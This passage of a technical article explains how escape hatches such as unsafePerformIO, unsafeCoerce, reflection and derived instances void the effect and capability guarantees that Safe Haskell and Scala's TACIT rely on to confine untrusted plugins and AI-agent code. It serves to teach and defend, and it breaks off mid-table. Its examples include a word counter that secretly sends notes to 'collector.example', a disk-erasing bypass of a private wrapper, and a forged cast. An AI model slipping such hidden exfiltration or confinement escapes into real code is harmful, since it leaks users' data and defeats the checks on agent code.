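# Escape Hatches That Void Effect and Capability Guarantees in Typed Languages

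## What effect and capability types promise

An escape hatch is a construct that a typed language's designers deliberately include to let code do what the type system would otherwise forbid or record. Most typed languages have several. They cause little trouble in everyday programming, and much fast or low-level library code depends on them. They matter more when someone runs code written by a stranger or by an *agent* (a language model that writes and runs code to carry out a task) and relies on the compiler's type checks to limit what that code can do.

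A type describes what kind of value an expression produces, and the compiler rejects programs whose types do not fit together. In most languages, a function's type covers only its inputs and result, so a function from a file name to a number may also delete a directory without its type showing this. Anything that code does besides returning a value is an *effect*. Code is *pure* if it has no effects and always gives the same result for the same input. Some languages use *effect types*, which record the effects that code may cause. Others use *capabilities*, which are unforgeable values that code must hold to use a resource such as a file or a network connection.

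Suppose a note-keeping program accepts plugins from strangers. One plugin counts the words in the user's notes. Its only permission is to read files in `/notes`, so it must not write files, use the network or open files elsewhere.

### The plugin with an effect type

In Haskell, a value of type `Int` is a whole number, while a value of type `IO Int` is a computation that yields a whole number when run and may also read files, open connections or delete data. Library functions that touch the outside world have `IO` in their result types, and ordinary pure code has no sanctioned way to run such a computation and take the result. A plugin of type `String -> Int` is therefore confined to turning text into a number.

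The word counter has to fetch its own text, though, and `IO` would give it far too much, because one type covers every effect alike. Terei, Mazières and colleagues (2012), in *Safe Haskell*, a paper on running untrusted Haskell code, deal with this by defining a restricted version of `IO`, which they call `RIO`. Cut down to the word counter, the host program's module looks roughly like this, leaving out some routine code for chaining steps together:

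```haskell
module PluginAPI (RIO, runRIO, readNote) where

newtype RIO a = UnsafeRIO (IO a)

runRIO :: RIO a -> IO a
runRIO (UnsafeRIO io) = io

readNote :: FilePath -> RIO String
readNote path = UnsafeRIO (do
  ok <- inNotesFolder path
  if ok then readFile path else return "")
```

`UnsafeRIO` wraps any `IO` computation as an `RIO` one, but other modules cannot see it because the export list on the top line omits it. The host accepts only plugins of type `RIO Int`, and a plugin can build such a value only from pure code and `readNote`, which checks every path before it reads.

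These guarantees all depend on *encapsulation*, the rule that the private parts of a module or class are reachable only through its public functions. A plugin that could access `UnsafeRIO` could wrap a command that erases the disk, and the result would still have type `RIO Int`.

### The plugin with a capability

In the other style, the host passes the plugin an object. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) describes the object-capability model behind this style, in which a reference to an object both identifies a resource and carries the right to use it. Code gets a reference by creating the object or by receiving the reference from other code that already has references to both the object and the recipient.

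Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use the language Scala to confine AI agents in this way, in a system named TACIT. A call to its function `requestFileSystem("/notes")` creates a `FileSystem` object for that folder, and the object refuses paths outside the folder at run time. Since it can also write, the host in the example puts it inside a smaller object that can only read:

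```scala
class NoteReader(fs: FileSystem^):
  def read(path: String): String = fs.access(path).read()

def plugin(notes: NoteReader^): Int
```

The mark `^` makes the compiler track the value as a capability (Scala calls this capture checking). The plugin can call `read`, but `fs` stays private inside the wrapper. The plugin cannot request a wider folder, because `requestFileSystem` requires a further capability that the host keeps. It also cannot save `fs` for later, because the compiler rejects any result whose type still refers to `fs` after the host's block of code has ended.

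These precautions fail if the plugin can open files without the object. Miller and colleagues use the term *ambient authority* for power that code exercises without selecting it. In their example, a program calls Unix `open()` with a file name and no credentials, and the request succeeds or fails. In ordinary Java, the `File` constructor likewise turns any string into an object that can read, write or delete the file of that name.

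Mettler, Wagner and Close (2010) built *Joe-E*, a subset of Java without ambient authority. Much of their work was deciding by hand which methods in Java's standard library to allow. A `File` object for a directory should give access only to that directory and whatever lies below it. But its `getParentFile()` method returns the directory above, so a program given one directory can reach the whole disk. Another constructor takes a directory and a file name, but treats the name as an absolute path when the directory is null, so Mettler and colleagues wrapped it in a function that checks for null. They call this manual selection a substantial weakness of their approach, since a single method allowed by mistake is enough to defeat the other restrictions. A review of the similar list for E, an older capability language, had found several such mistakes.

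Effect and capability types are closely related. *Recovering Purity with Comonads and Capabilities* (2019) starts from a language in which functions may print freely and adds a type for expressions that have no access to capabilities. Code without capabilities cannot cause effects, so this addition is enough to recover pure functions. Scala's notation makes a similar distinction between functions of type `String -> Int`, which hold no capabilities, and functions of type `String => Int`, which may hold any.

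### The three properties

Odersky and colleagues require three properties of a language before its types can confine untrusted code.

*Capability safety* means that code cannot forge a capability and that types always record the capabilities code needs. The plugin cannot create a `FileSystem` from a number, and if a function inside it uses `notes`, that function's type still records this when the function is passed elsewhere.

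*Capability completeness* means that capabilities regulate every effect that matters for safety, so that `notes` is the plugin's only way to access a file. Odersky and colleagues leave out effects that the system can contain at run time, mainly exceptions, which are errors that interrupt a program. Dividing by zero or running out of memory can raise an exception anywhere, so banning exceptions in the types would be impractical. TACIT instead catches them at the edge of the agent's code and turns them into ordinary values.

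*Local purity* means that the type system can express that a computation uses only a given set of capabilities, possibly none. Suppose a later version of the plugin may also contact a dictionary server, and some of the notes are confidential. The host can choose to pass confidential text only to functions of type `String -> Int`. The compiler then rejects any such function that uses the network, even though the rest of the plugin may use it. A permission list cannot prevent the leak, because it allows the plugin both to read the notes and to contact the server, and so does not stop it from sending the text of a note to the server.

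Languages meet these requirements unevenly. Odersky and colleagues grant that local purity is obtainable in Haskell but note that Haskell has no native object capabilities, and they describe Joe-E as relying on run-time mechanisms alone. That description slightly understates Joe-E's static checking. Mettler and colleagues give the example of an untrusted image decoder whose interface requires it to be immutable. Joe-E's checker verifies before the program runs that the decoder contains only immutable data, so the decoder cannot hold a capability or keep any data from one image to the next. This is close to local purity for whole objects, though not for individual functions inside a program.

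Some behaviour falls outside these guarantees. Joe-E does not limit how much processor time or memory code uses, so a word counter that loops forever does not violate its rules. TACIT does not cover information leaked through timing.

### Why one reachable escape hatch is enough

Written out for the Haskell plugin, the guarantee is a statement about all programs:

> For every program *p*: if *p* has type `RIO Int`, then running *p* reads files in `/notes` and has no other effect.

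Because the guarantee covers every *p*, the host need not read the plugin, test it or know who wrote it. But one counterexample makes the guarantee false, and a hostile author can choose *p* to be that counterexample.

Type soundness, the theorem that "well-typed programs cannot go wrong", is also conditional. *A Logical Approach to Type Soundness* (Timany, Krebbers and colleagues, 2024) points out that its standard form applies only to programs that are well typed in their entirety. If any part of a program uses an unsafe feature, the theorem guarantees nothing about the program as a whole. Similarly, according to *Object-Capability as a Means of Permission and Authority in Software Systems* (2019), programmers can use Java in a capability-safe way if the whole program follows certain restrictions.

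Mettler and colleagues give the example of a small Java class for a log, with one private field and one public method that appends a line. Code anywhere else in the application can use reflection (the facility by which a program inspects and manipulates its own classes) to access the private field, so a reviewer has to read the whole application, not just this class, to be sure that nobody can erase an entry.

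Haskell programmers rely on pure types every day although full Haskell does not guarantee them, and Terei and colleagues attribute this to community norms. When programmers are honest, what matters is how often they misuse an escape hatch and whether reviewers notice. Against a hostile plugin, all that matters is whether the plugin can reach a hatch, either by naming it directly or by calling a library function that exposes the same power. An unsafe function in a module that the plugin cannot import does no harm unless the plugin can reach it through such a library function.

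Language designers can therefore leave the escape hatches in place and control which code can use them. A *safe subset* is the part of a language that remains once the compiler rejects the escape hatches. Code in the subset may still call a *trusted module*, which uses escape hatches internally and whose author vouches that its public interface is safe. Safe Haskell, the compiler extension that Terei and colleagues describe, labels modules as safe, trustworthy or unsafe. The *trusted base* is everything that must be correct for the guarantee to hold: the compiler, the runtime that executes the program, and the trusted modules.

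For the word counter, the trusted base also contains `inNotesFolder`. Haskell's and Scala's types don't represent folders. They ensure that the plugin goes through the path check, but the check itself is ordinary code. If it misses a `..` that leads to a parent directory, the plugin can reach files outside the notes folder without using an escape hatch.

Effect and capability guarantees can also fail because of a *soundness hole*, an error in a type system or its checker that lets a forbidden program pass without any declared escape hatch. Terei and colleagues describe one in Generalised Newtype Deriving, a popular Haskell extension, which at the time let a program alter values that another module meant to protect. A soundness hole is as useful to a hostile author as an escape hatch, but designers intend to fix soundness holes and keep escape hatches.

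### Three kinds of escape hatch

Some hatches give a computation a false type. Haskell's `unsafePerformIO` presents the result of an `IO` computation as a pure value, so the word counter could send the notes to a server during what looks like a pure calculation. In Scala, an unchecked cast, which makes the compiler treat a value as having another type, can do the same by relabelling a function that uses the network as `String -> Int`. Odersky and colleagues describe such features as "forgetting" capabilities. These hatches break the half of capability safety that records which capabilities code needs. They also break local purity, because the compiler's only evidence that a function is pure is its type.

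Other hatches give access to private state. Reflection can pull the `FileSystem` object out of `NoteReader`, which lets the plugin write as well as read. Terei and colleagues list an attack on their own `RIO` type that uses Template Haskell, which generates code during compilation, to reach the hidden wrapper. Deserialization, which rebuilds objects from stored bytes, also belongs here if it bypasses the checks that a class makes when it creates an object. In *Integrity by Default*, a draft proposal for the Java platform, Pressler, Buckley and Reinhold (2023) concede that Java's own unsafe interfaces can undermine the protection developers expect for their code and data. Odersky and colleagues have no separate heading for encapsulation. The damage falls under capability safety because the plugin gains a power that nobody gave it.

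The remaining hatches run code outside the language. A program can call code written in another language, usually C, through a *foreign function interface* (FFI), or it can start another program. The type checker does not check the C code or the child process. If the word counter may run an external command, that command can read any file the operating system lets it read, without holding `notes` or any other capability, which breaks capability completeness. Odersky and colleagues accept this limit for TACIT, where the static guarantee shrinks to whatever the list of permitted commands ensures once an agent starts an external process.

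The categories overlap. Native code running in the same process can overwrite memory and so forge references, which is why Mettler and colleagues list their ban on native methods under unforgeability. An effectful foreign function declared in Haskell with a pure type both leaves the language and has a false type.

Ambient authority breaks capability completeness, but it is not on this list because it comes from ordinary features, such as Java's `File` constructor, that nobody marks as unsafe. A safe subset that removed only the declared hatches would leave it in place. Exceptions, another ordinary feature, can also leak capabilities. In an example from Mettler and colleagues, a component lends its private capability to a helper, the helper throws an exception containing the capability, and a caller further up catches it. Joe-E therefore requires exceptions to be immutable, and TACIT forbids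 storing capabilities in them.

### Why languages have escape hatches

Speed is one reason to use escape hatches. Haskell's `ByteString` library presents text as a pure, list-like value, with only pure functions in its interface, but stores it as packed bytes and reads them directly from memory. A version without unsafe operations would be much slower. Similarly, a function that keeps earlier answers in a hidden table returns the same results as one that recomputes them, but filling the table is an effect, and the type checker cannot verify that it is harmless.

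Languages also need escape hatches to reach the operating system. Some code below `readNote` and `NoteReader` has to call it, and capabilities cannot regulate the code that implements them. For this reason, Mettler and colleagues wrote parts of Joe-E's library in unrestricted Java.

Escape hatches also let programs use existing libraries. Haskell, for example, lets a programmer import C's sine function as a pure function. That declaration is correct, but the compiler can't check it and would accept the same declaration for a C function that deletes files. Odersky and colleagues call casts and reflection necessary escape hatches in general programming, but forbid both in code that an untrusted agent writes.

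## Running effects inside pure code

Haskell's `unsafePerformIO`, which presents the result of an `IO` computation as a pure value, has the type `IO a -> a`, where `a` stands for any type. With it, the word counter's author can also copy the notes to a server (`sendTo` stands for any function that sends text over the network):

```haskell
countWords :: String -> Int
countWords text = unsafePerformIO (do
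  sendTo "collector.example" text
  return (length (words text)))
```

`unsafePerformIO` turns the part in parentheses from an `IO Int` into an `Int`, so the compiler accepts `countWords` as a function of type `String -> Int`. A host that passes confidential text only to functions of that type gets no protection.

### How the function works

GHC, the main Haskell compiler, defines `IO` as a function:

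```haskell
newtype IO a = IO (State# RealWorld -> (# State# RealWorld, a #))
```

The function's argument is a *state token*, a value that stands for the state of the outside world. The function returns a new token together with the result. (The `#` signs mark low-level values and make no difference here.)

Tokens keep effects in order. FP Complete (2015), a Haskell consultancy, explains this with a program that prints 3 and then 7. GHC can reorder calculations that do not depend on each other, and printing 7 does not use the result of printing 3. But the first print returns a token that the second needs as its argument, so the second cannot start early. The tokens carry no data and, according to GHC's compiler notes, have no representation at run time.

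Leaving out two safeguards, which come up below, the definition of `unsafePerformIO` is:

```haskell
unsafePerformIO (IO m) =
  case runRW# m of (# _, result #) -> result
```

Here `m` is the function inside the `IO` computation. `runRW#` calls it with a token that did not come from any earlier step of the program. The function returns a new token and a result, and the underscore discards the token, leaving only the result.

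Steps inside the computation stay in order, so `countWords` sends the text before it returns the number. But no other part of the program receives the discarded token, so nothing determines when the computation runs relative to everything else.

A related function, `unsafeInterleaveIO`, has type `IO a -> IO a`. It gives the current token to a computation and passes the same token to the next step, which proceeds without waiting. The computation runs only when something needs its result. Haskell's lazy file reading works this way. The program receives a string immediately, and the file is read as the program consumes the string. The type still includes `IO`, but the effect happens later, inside what looks like pure code. An alternative standard library, linear-base, gives `IO` a stricter type that requires each computation to use its token exactly once, as a contributor to the forum thread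 *How RealWorld passes to the main?* points out. Passing the same token to two steps breaks that rule.

### What the compiler does to a hidden effect

Terei and colleagues show the trouble with a function that reads the clock. Let `usec` be the `IO` computation that returns the system time in microseconds, and define:

```haskell
f x = x + unsafePerformIO usec
```

The expressions `let x = f 3 in x + x` and `f 3 + f 3` can give different results. The first calls `f` once. If the clock reads *t*, then `x` is 3 + *t* and the sum is 2(3 + *t*), which is always even. The second can read the clock twice, getting *t*₁ and *t*₂, so the sum is 6 + *t*₁ + *t*₂. With readings of 100 and 101, that is 207.

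If `f` were really pure, the two expressions would always be equal, and GHC could replace either with the other. It relies on this kind of equality when it optimises code, which can change how often a hidden effect happens:

| What GHC may do | Effect on the hidden computation | Precaution |
|---|---|---|
| Evaluate a value only when something needs it, then keep the result (lazy evaluation) | It runs late, once or never | None: this is how Haskell works |
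| Copy a definition into the places that use it (inlining) | It may run more than once | A `NOINLINE` mark on the function |
| Merge two identical expressions (common subexpression elimination) | Two effects become one | The compiler flag `-fno-cse` |
| Move an expression out of a function if it does not depend on the argument (let-floating) | All calls share one run | The flag `-fno-full-laziness`, or code that uses the argument |

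The *GHC.IO.Unsafe* documentation on Hackage, Haskell's package archive, lists these precautions and describes them as necessary for GHC but possibly insufficient. The last row applies to the clock example. Since `unsafePerformIO usec` does not mention `x`, GHC may move it out of `f` and read the clock once for the whole program. Then `f 3 + f 3` is always even too. The same source code can give different answers depending on the optimisation settings.

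GHC's own definition of `unsafePerformIO` includes a safeguard against the optimiser. It exists because of a function that stores its earlier answers in a table. The function locks the table, records the new answer as a calculation not yet performed, unlocks the table and returns the answer. Lazy evaluation postpones the calculation until after the unlocking. But when GHC worked out that the program would certainly need the answer, it could perform the calculation while the table was still locked. If the calculation called the same function again, the program waited forever for a lock it already held. The safeguard hides from the optimiser the fact that the program needs the result.

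The other safeguard checks whether two threads on a multiprocessor have started evaluating the same expression. This check takes time, so GHC also offers `unsafeDupablePerformIO`, which omits it. According to Hackage, that version may run a computation several times, or stop one copy partway without raising an exception, so code that must clean up after itself cannot rely on it.

For speed, the text library has a version of `unsafePerformIO` that GHC can inline. A comment in Hackage's *Data.Text.Internal.Unsafe* marks it "Very unsafe" and warns programmers not to allocate memory inside it. If the optimiser merged two allocations, two separate pieces of text could end up sharing the same memory.

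This unpredictability does not protect a host from a hostile plugin. `countWords` needs to send each text only once, and it does so as soon as the host uses the word count.

### Deriving an unchecked cast

`unsafePerformIO` also breaks type safety, which is less obvious from its type. The derivation needs an `IORef`, Haskell's mutable cell, and a cell that holds a list:

```haskell
{-# NOINLINE cell #-}
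cell :: IORef [a]
cell = unsafePerformIO (newIORef [])

cast :: a -> b
cast x = unsafePerformIO (do
  writeIORef cell [x]
  [y] <- readIORef cell
  return y)
```

An empty list can have any element type, so `[]` can be a list of numbers or a list of characters. Likewise, `newIORef []` can create a cell for any element type. In normal `IO` code, each run creates a new cell and the compiler gives that cell one element type, so a program that writes numbers to it cannot then read characters from it.

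`unsafePerformIO` makes `cell` look like a pure value, so the compiler lets each use choose its own element type. But GHC evaluates `cell` once at run time and keeps the result, so every use shares the same cell. `cast` writes to that cell at type `a` and reads from it at type `b`, so it returns its argument unchanged under any type the caller chooses.

The example in the Hackage documentation writes the number 42 to such a cell, reads it back as text and crashes. According to the documentation, programmers can also build a general cast this way, and the programmer ppetr published a worked version.

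The cast also defeats encapsulation. The private `UnsafeRIO` wrapper from the first section adds nothing at run time, so an `IO Int` and an `RIO Int` are identical in memory. A plugin can `cast` a computation that erases the disk to type `RIO Int` without using the wrapper. One function that appears to concern only effects therefore breaks purity, type safety and encapsulation.

Haskell also supplies the cast directly, as `unsafeCoerce`, with the same type `a -> b`. Terei and colleagues use it to add a `Float` to an `Int`, which gives a wrong answer at best. Cardano's *Unsafe.Coerce*, a copy of the standard documentation, describes a legitimate use: converting an `Int` to a catch-all type, storing it in a list and later converting it back. This is safe as long as the programmer remembers the original type.

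OCaml's equivalent is `Obj.magic`, which also returns its argument unchanged under any type. It does less damage to guarantees about effects because OCaml makes few of them. An ordinary OCaml function may write files without its type showing this. But `Obj.magic` breaks type safety and the privacy of a module's data, as `unsafeCoerce` does. OCaml blocks the shared-cell trick with a typing rule called the value restriction, which gives a newly created cell a single element type. Haskell does not need such a rule as long as cells are created only inside `IO`.

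### Similar hatches for effect types and capabilities

Types in Koka and Flix distinguish between kinds of effect, whereas Haskell puts them all under `IO`. Koka's `unsafe-total` calls a function that may have any effects and gives the result a type with none. Flix's `unchecked_cast` can change the effect that the compiler records for an expression, or remove it. Scala's capture checker has `caps.unsafe.unsafeAssumePure`, which removes captured capabilities from a value's type.

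These languages normally evaluate a function's arguments before the call, so a hidden effect tends to happen where the programmer wrote it. This avoids much of the confusion about timing that laziness causes in Haskell. But the type is still false, and an optimiser that relied on it could delete or merge calls.

The Scala function gives a hostile author less than the others do. Haskell code can import a function that opens a network connection without anyone's permission, and only the `IO` type keeps a pure function from using it. `unsafePerformIO` therefore gives a plugin every power in the libraries it can import. `unsafeAssumePure` only hides a capability that the code already holds. If capabilities control all access to the network, a plugin without a network capability can't use `unsafeAssumePure` to get that access. But a plugin that may contact a dictionary server can hide that capability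 and so receive confidential text, which is why TACIT rejects unchecked casts in agents' code.

### Which hidden effects are harmless

According to Hackage, a computation inside `unsafePerformIO` should have no side effects and should not depend on its environment. *Memo functions*, which keep earlier answers in a table, and `ByteString` both break the rule against side effects because they change memory. Terei and colleagues add that lazy evaluation itself depends on a hidden effect, in which the runtime overwrites an unevaluated expression with its value to avoid recalculating it.

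In all these cases, nobody who uses the function can tell that the effect took place. Some definitions of *side effect* exclude such hidden effects. *Formalization and Implementation of Safe Destination Passing in Pure Functional Programming Settings* (2026), for example, counts changes to memory as side effects only if the user can observe them.

The argument for a memo function depends on an invariant, a condition that stays true throughout. *A Monadic Framework for Relational Verification* (2017) contains a proof for a function *g* and its memoised version, with the invariant that every pair (*x*, *y*) in the table satisfies *y* = *g*(*x*). An empty table satisfies it. If the table already contains *x*, the stored answer is correct. If not, the function calculates *g*(*x*) and stores a correct pair, so the invariant still holds. The memoised function therefore gives the same answer as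 *g* on every input, whatever calls came before.

*Checking Observational Purity of Procedures* (2019) applies similar reasoning to procedures with hidden state. One example calculates factorials and remembers only the factorial of 19, in a variable that starts at −1. The invariant is that the variable holds either −1 or 19 times the factorial of 18. If every run preserves the invariant and no two runs with the same input give different outputs, the procedure behaves like a mathematical function. The clock-reading `f` fails this test.

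But `countWords` passes this test, because it returns the right number for every text and no code that calls it can detect the message to the server. So the test must also include observers outside the program. The effect must leave no trace on the disk and be invisible to other programs and to anyone on the network.

A memo function returns faster when it is called again with the same input, so code with access to a clock may be able to find out which inputs someone has already tried. Definitions of purity usually ignore this timing difference. *Type, Ability, and Effect Systems* (2025), for example, counts only simple values such as integers and booleans as observable results. A memo table shared by confidential and untrusted code can satisfy such a definition and still leak information.

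### The proof for `runST`

Haskell has a function that hides effects and is safe for every argument the compiler accepts. Launchbury and Peyton Jones introduced it in 1994 for algorithms that need mutable memory internally. Computations of type `ST s a` can create, read and write mutable cells but cannot touch files or the network. `runST` runs one and returns a pure result:

```haskell
runST :: (forall s. ST s a) -> a
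```

The type variable `s` labels the region of memory that the computation uses, and every cell the computation creates carries that label. The `forall s` means the computation must work for any label, so it cannot use a cell from elsewhere, which would carry a particular one. The result type `a` cannot mention `s`, so no cell can leave. For example, the compiler rejects `runST (newSTRef 42)` because it would return the new cell. It accepts a function that calculates Fibonacci numbers by repeatedly updating two cells, since that function returns only a number.

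Launchbury and Peyton Jones argued informally that this keeps the rest of the language pure. *A Logical Relation for Monadic Encapsulation of State* (Timany, Stefanesco and colleagues, 2018) proved it for a model language called STLang. The regions exist only in STLang's types. At run time, all cells share one global memory, or *heap*, and writes change it in place, as in a real implementation. Earlier proofs used models that divided memory into separate regions, which made the isolation easier to prove.

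To make "no caller can observe the effect" exact, Timany and colleagues use a standard notion called *contextual equivalence*:

> Two expressions *e*₁ and *e*₂ are equivalent if, for every well-typed program *C* with a gap in it and all starting heaps *h* and *h*′, *C* with *e*₁ in the gap terminates from *h* exactly when *C* with *e*₂ in the gap terminates from *h*′.

Any difference that a program can detect can become a difference in termination, because *C* can be any program, including one that examines the result and loops forever for some values but not others.

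One of the equivalences they prove says that calculating an expression once and using it twice is the same as calculating it twice:

> `let x = e in (x, x)` is equivalent to `(e, e)`

The clock example breaks this law. If `e` is `f 3`, and *C* adds the two numbers and loops forever when the sum is odd, the left side always terminates but the right side sometimes does not. In STLang the law holds for every well-typed `e`, even one that uses `runST` internally. Under another equivalence, the order in which a program evaluates two pure expressions does not matter.

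Timany and colleagues also prove a theorem they call State Independence. If a well-typed pure expression terminates from some heap, it terminates from every heap, and the final heap contains everything that was in the starting heap, unchanged. The expression may create new cells but cannot read or write existing ones. They checked all the proofs with the proof checker Coq, in about 12,500 lines.

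The 2018 proof has limits as evidence about Haskell. STLang evaluates arguments before calling a function, whereas Haskell is lazy, and Timany and colleagues leave a lazy version to future work. They also prove only a particular list of equivalences. In *Purity of an ST Monad* (2022), Jacobs, Devriese and Timany prove for a simpler language that adding `ST` preserves every equivalence that held without it, so a programmer in that language can reason about pure code as if `ST` did not exist. They too state that their result does not apply directly to Haskell. *Pure Borrow* (2026) addresses mutation by several threads at once, which the 2018 proof also left open. It extends Linear Haskell, a version of the language that can require code to use a value exactly once, and relates a description of each program's physical behaviour in memory to a description of its mathematical meaning.

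GHC implements `runST` and `unsafePerformIO` in almost the same way. Both supply a token, run the computation and discard the token that comes back, but their types differ. The type of `runST` excludes harmful computations, so a host can safely expose it to untrusted code. `unsafePerformIO` accepts any `IO` computation, so someone has to show separately for each use that observers can't detect the effects, as researchers have done for Rust libraries that contain unsafe code. Safe Haskell therefore forbids `unsafePerformIO` in modules compiled as safe, according to GHC's user guide.

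The proofs also assume a language without unchecked casts. In GHC, `IO` and `ST` computations are both functions on state tokens, and the tokens differ only in their type label. A plugin with access to `unsafeCoerce` can relabel any `IO` computation as an `ST` one and pass it to `runST`, which then does everything `unsafePerformIO` does.

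## Safe Haskell

A host that accepts Haskell plugins needs a compiler that rejects `unsafePerformIO`, `unsafeCoerce` and anything else with the same power. It should still let plugins use libraries such as `ByteString`, which call unsafe functions internally. GHC has had a mode for this, Safe Haskell, since version 7.2. David Terei and David Mazières of Stanford designed it with Simon Marlow and Simon Peyton Jones of Microsoft Research. They drew on Modula-3, a research language from the 1980s in which an unsafe module can present a safe interface to the rest of a program.

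### The five guarantees

Code in the *safe language*, the subset of Haskell that GHC accepts in this mode, has five properties, provided that the compiler and the trusted modules are correct:

- **Type safety.** Well-typed programs do not go wrong.
- **Referential transparency.** A function with a pure type really is pure, although it may loop forever or raise an exception.
- **Module encapsulation.** Other modules can create and inspect values of an abstract type only through the functions that its own module exports.
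- **Modular reasoning.** Adding an import to a module does not change the meaning of existing code that does not depend on the imported module.
- **Semantic consistency.** An expression that compiles in both the safe language and full Haskell has the same meaning in both.

The `RIO` interface for the word counter depends directly on type safety, referential transparency and encapsulation. Modular reasoning protects the host's code, because the host imports the plugin's module.

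GHC's user guide illustrates the danger with a *type class*, a set of functions that each type can implement in its own way. Each implementation is called an *instance*. The host has an instance that turns a list of any kind into the text `[a]`, and a stranger's module adds one for lists of whole numbers that produces `[Int]`. GHC prefers the more specific instance, so merely importing the stranger's module would change the result of the host's existing call on `[1,2,3,4]`. If the function were used to hide parts of a note in a log, the stranger would control which parts were hidden. GHC refuses to compile the call when the host's module is itself in the safe language or its author has labelled it trustworthy.

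### Which modules a plugin may import

Each module belongs to one of three classes. A *Safe* module is written in the safe language, and GHC checks this. A *Trustworthy* module may use any feature of Haskell, but its author claims that nobody can misuse its public interface. All other modules are *Unsafe*. Authors write the label at the top of the file, and a host can also impose the safe language on a plugin with the compiler flag `-XSafe`.

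A Safe module may import only modules that the person compiling the program trusts. Terei and colleagues define this recursively:

A user trusts a Safe module if they trust every module it imports directly. They trust a Trustworthy module if they trust the package it comes from and every module it imports with the keyword `safe`.

A *package* is a group of modules that an author distributes together. Suppose the word counter imports the module `Splitter` from a stranger's package, `textkit`. `Splitter` is Safe and imports only `Prelude`, the basic part of Haskell's standard library, which is Trustworthy and belongs to the package `base`. The host trusts `base`, so the rule allows `Prelude` and therefore `Splitter`. The host doesn't need to trust `textkit` or know who wrote it.

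Now suppose `Splitter`'s author speeds up the module with `unsafePerformIO`. It no longer compiles as Safe, so the author has to label it Trustworthy, and the word counter stops compiling until the host trusts `textkit`. The host therefore has to assess only the packages whose Trustworthy modules the plugin depends on.

The author of a Trustworthy module vouches for the modules it imports, except those imported with `import safe`. The user decides whether to trust those modules, and GHC checks them by the same rule it applies to the Trustworthy module.

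GHC ignores the condition about packages by default. The first release always enforced it, so libraries whose authors had labelled modules Safe failed to compile for users who had never marked any package as trusted. Terei and colleagues therefore put the check behind a flag, `-fpackage-trust`. Without the flag, GHC treats every package as trusted, so any author can get a module accepted by writing `Trustworthy` at the top. When Terei and colleagues queried `Data.ByteString` in GHC's interactive mode, it reported the package as untrusted and the module as trusted.

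Compiling libraries without the flag is harmless because the rule is recursive and a host can apply the full check when it compiles the plugin, though the host's developers must remember to enable it. Edward Yang's *Unintuitive facts about Safe Haskell* recommends always using the flag for untrusted code, but considers the default adequate for people who use Safe Haskell only to enforce good style.

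### Automatic inference

Few authors label their modules, so GHC infers a label. It marks an unlabelled module Safe if the module would compile as Safe, ignoring package trust, and Unsafe otherwise. It never infers Trustworthy, because that label records a person's claim that the module is safe to use.

Safety inference can expose private code. Suppose the host's programmer exports `UnsafeRIO` from a helper module so that several parts of the host can share it. The helper uses no unsafe feature, so GHC infers that it is Safe. A plugin that can import the helper can then wrap any `IO` computation as an `RIO` one. To prevent this, the programmer has to label the helper Unsafe by hand. Yang gives a similar example of a web library whose internal module exposes the constructor of its type for escaped HTML. Untrusted code could use the constructor to insert a script into a page.

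### Four attacks on `RIO`

Terei and colleagues describe four ways in which a plugin could break out of `RIO` if the host compiled it as ordinary Haskell.

The plugin could use `unsafePerformIO` to run any `IO` computation inside an `RIO` one. A Safe plugin cannot import the function because GHC classifies its module, `System.IO.Unsafe`, as Unsafe.

A foreign import could declare that a C function with side effects is pure. The safe language therefore requires every foreign import to have an `IO` type. This applies to harmless functions too, so if a Safe module imports C's sine function directly, calling it gives an `IO` computation instead of a number.

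Another attack uses `Typeable`, a type class that gives each type a unique representation at run time. A library function uses it for checked casts:

```haskell
cast :: (Typeable a, Typeable b) => a -> Maybe b
```

`cast` compares the representations of the two types. If they match, it returns the value under the new type, using an unsafe cast internally; otherwise it returns `Nothing`. In 2012 GHC could generate `Typeable` instances but also accepted handwritten ones. A plugin could define an instance for `RIO` that returned the representation of `IO`, and `cast` would then convert any `IO` computation into an `RIO` one. Safe Haskell accepted only the instances that GHC had generated.

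The remaining attack uses Template Haskell, the code generator mentioned in the first section. It can refer to names that another module doesn't export, so a plugin could use it to access `UnsafeRIO`. The safe language excludes Template Haskell altogether.

These rules restrict the plugin, but the host's interface is still up to its author, and the published example contains a mistake. The paper and the current user guide both define the wrapper with a named field:

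```haskell
newtype RIO a = UnsafeRIO { runRIO :: IO a }
```

The module exports `runRIO` but not `UnsafeRIO`. However, Haskell lets any module that can see a field's name replace the field's contents, so a plugin can write `(return ()) { runRIO = eraseDisk }` and get an `RIO` computation that erases the disk, without using any unsafe feature. The `PluginAPI` module in the first section avoids this because its `runRIO` is an ordinary function, not a record field.

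### Breaking an abstract type with a derived instance

According to Terei and colleagues, many Haskell programmers would probably be surprised that Template Haskell and the Generalised Newtype Deriving extension can both break module boundaries. A `newtype` is a new type with the same representation in memory as an existing one. Generalised Newtype Deriving saves a lot of repetitive code by reusing the existing type's instances for the new type.

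Terei and colleagues attack a list type that should contain only elements greater than a fixed minimum:

```haskell
module MinList (MinList, newMinList, insertMinList) where

data MinList a = MinList a [a]

newMinList least = MinList least []

insertMinList list@(MinList least items) new
  | new > least = MinList least (new : items)
  | otherwise   = list
```

The constructor `MinList` is private, so other modules can add elements only through `insertMinList`, which checks them. The attacker defines a type class, an `Int` instance and a newtype:

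```haskell
class IntIso t where
  intIso :: c t -> c Int

instance IntIso Int where
  intIso x = x

newtype I = I Int deriving (Eq, IntIso)

instance Ord I where
  compare (I a) (I b) = compare b a
```

Here `c` stands for any container type. For `Int`, `intIso` has type `c Int -> c Int` and returns its argument. The `deriving` clause makes GHC reuse that function for `I`, where its type becomes `c I -> c Int`. The attacker can then relabel any container of `I` as a container of `Int`, even if its constructors are private, which no handwritten function could do.

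The last instance reverses the order of numbers for `I`. The attacker creates a `MinList` of `I` with minimum 1 and inserts 4, 0, 1, −5, 2 and 3. `insertMinList` compares them in the reversed order, so it accepts only 0 and −5. The attacker then uses `intIso` to convert the result to a `MinList Int` whose minimum is 1 but whose elements are −5 and 0. Inserting the same numbers directly into a `MinList Int` with minimum 1 gives a list of 4, 2 and 3.

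This is the soundness hole mentioned in the first section, and in 2012 Terei and colleagues expected GHC's developers to fix it. GHC has since added *role annotations*, which let an author state when the compiler may relabel a container. Adding `type role MinList nominal` to the module prevents the attack, but GHC allows relabelling for a type like `MinList` by default, and authors forget to add the line. For that reason, according to the user guide, the safe language still excludes Generalised Newtype Deriving. It also excludes the newer extension `DerivingVia` and the module `Data.Coerce`, which offers the same relabelling as an ordinary function.

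### What the safe language excludes

GHC's developers have changed several of the restrictions since 2012:

| Feature | What it can break | Rule in 2012 | Current rule |
|---|---|---|---|
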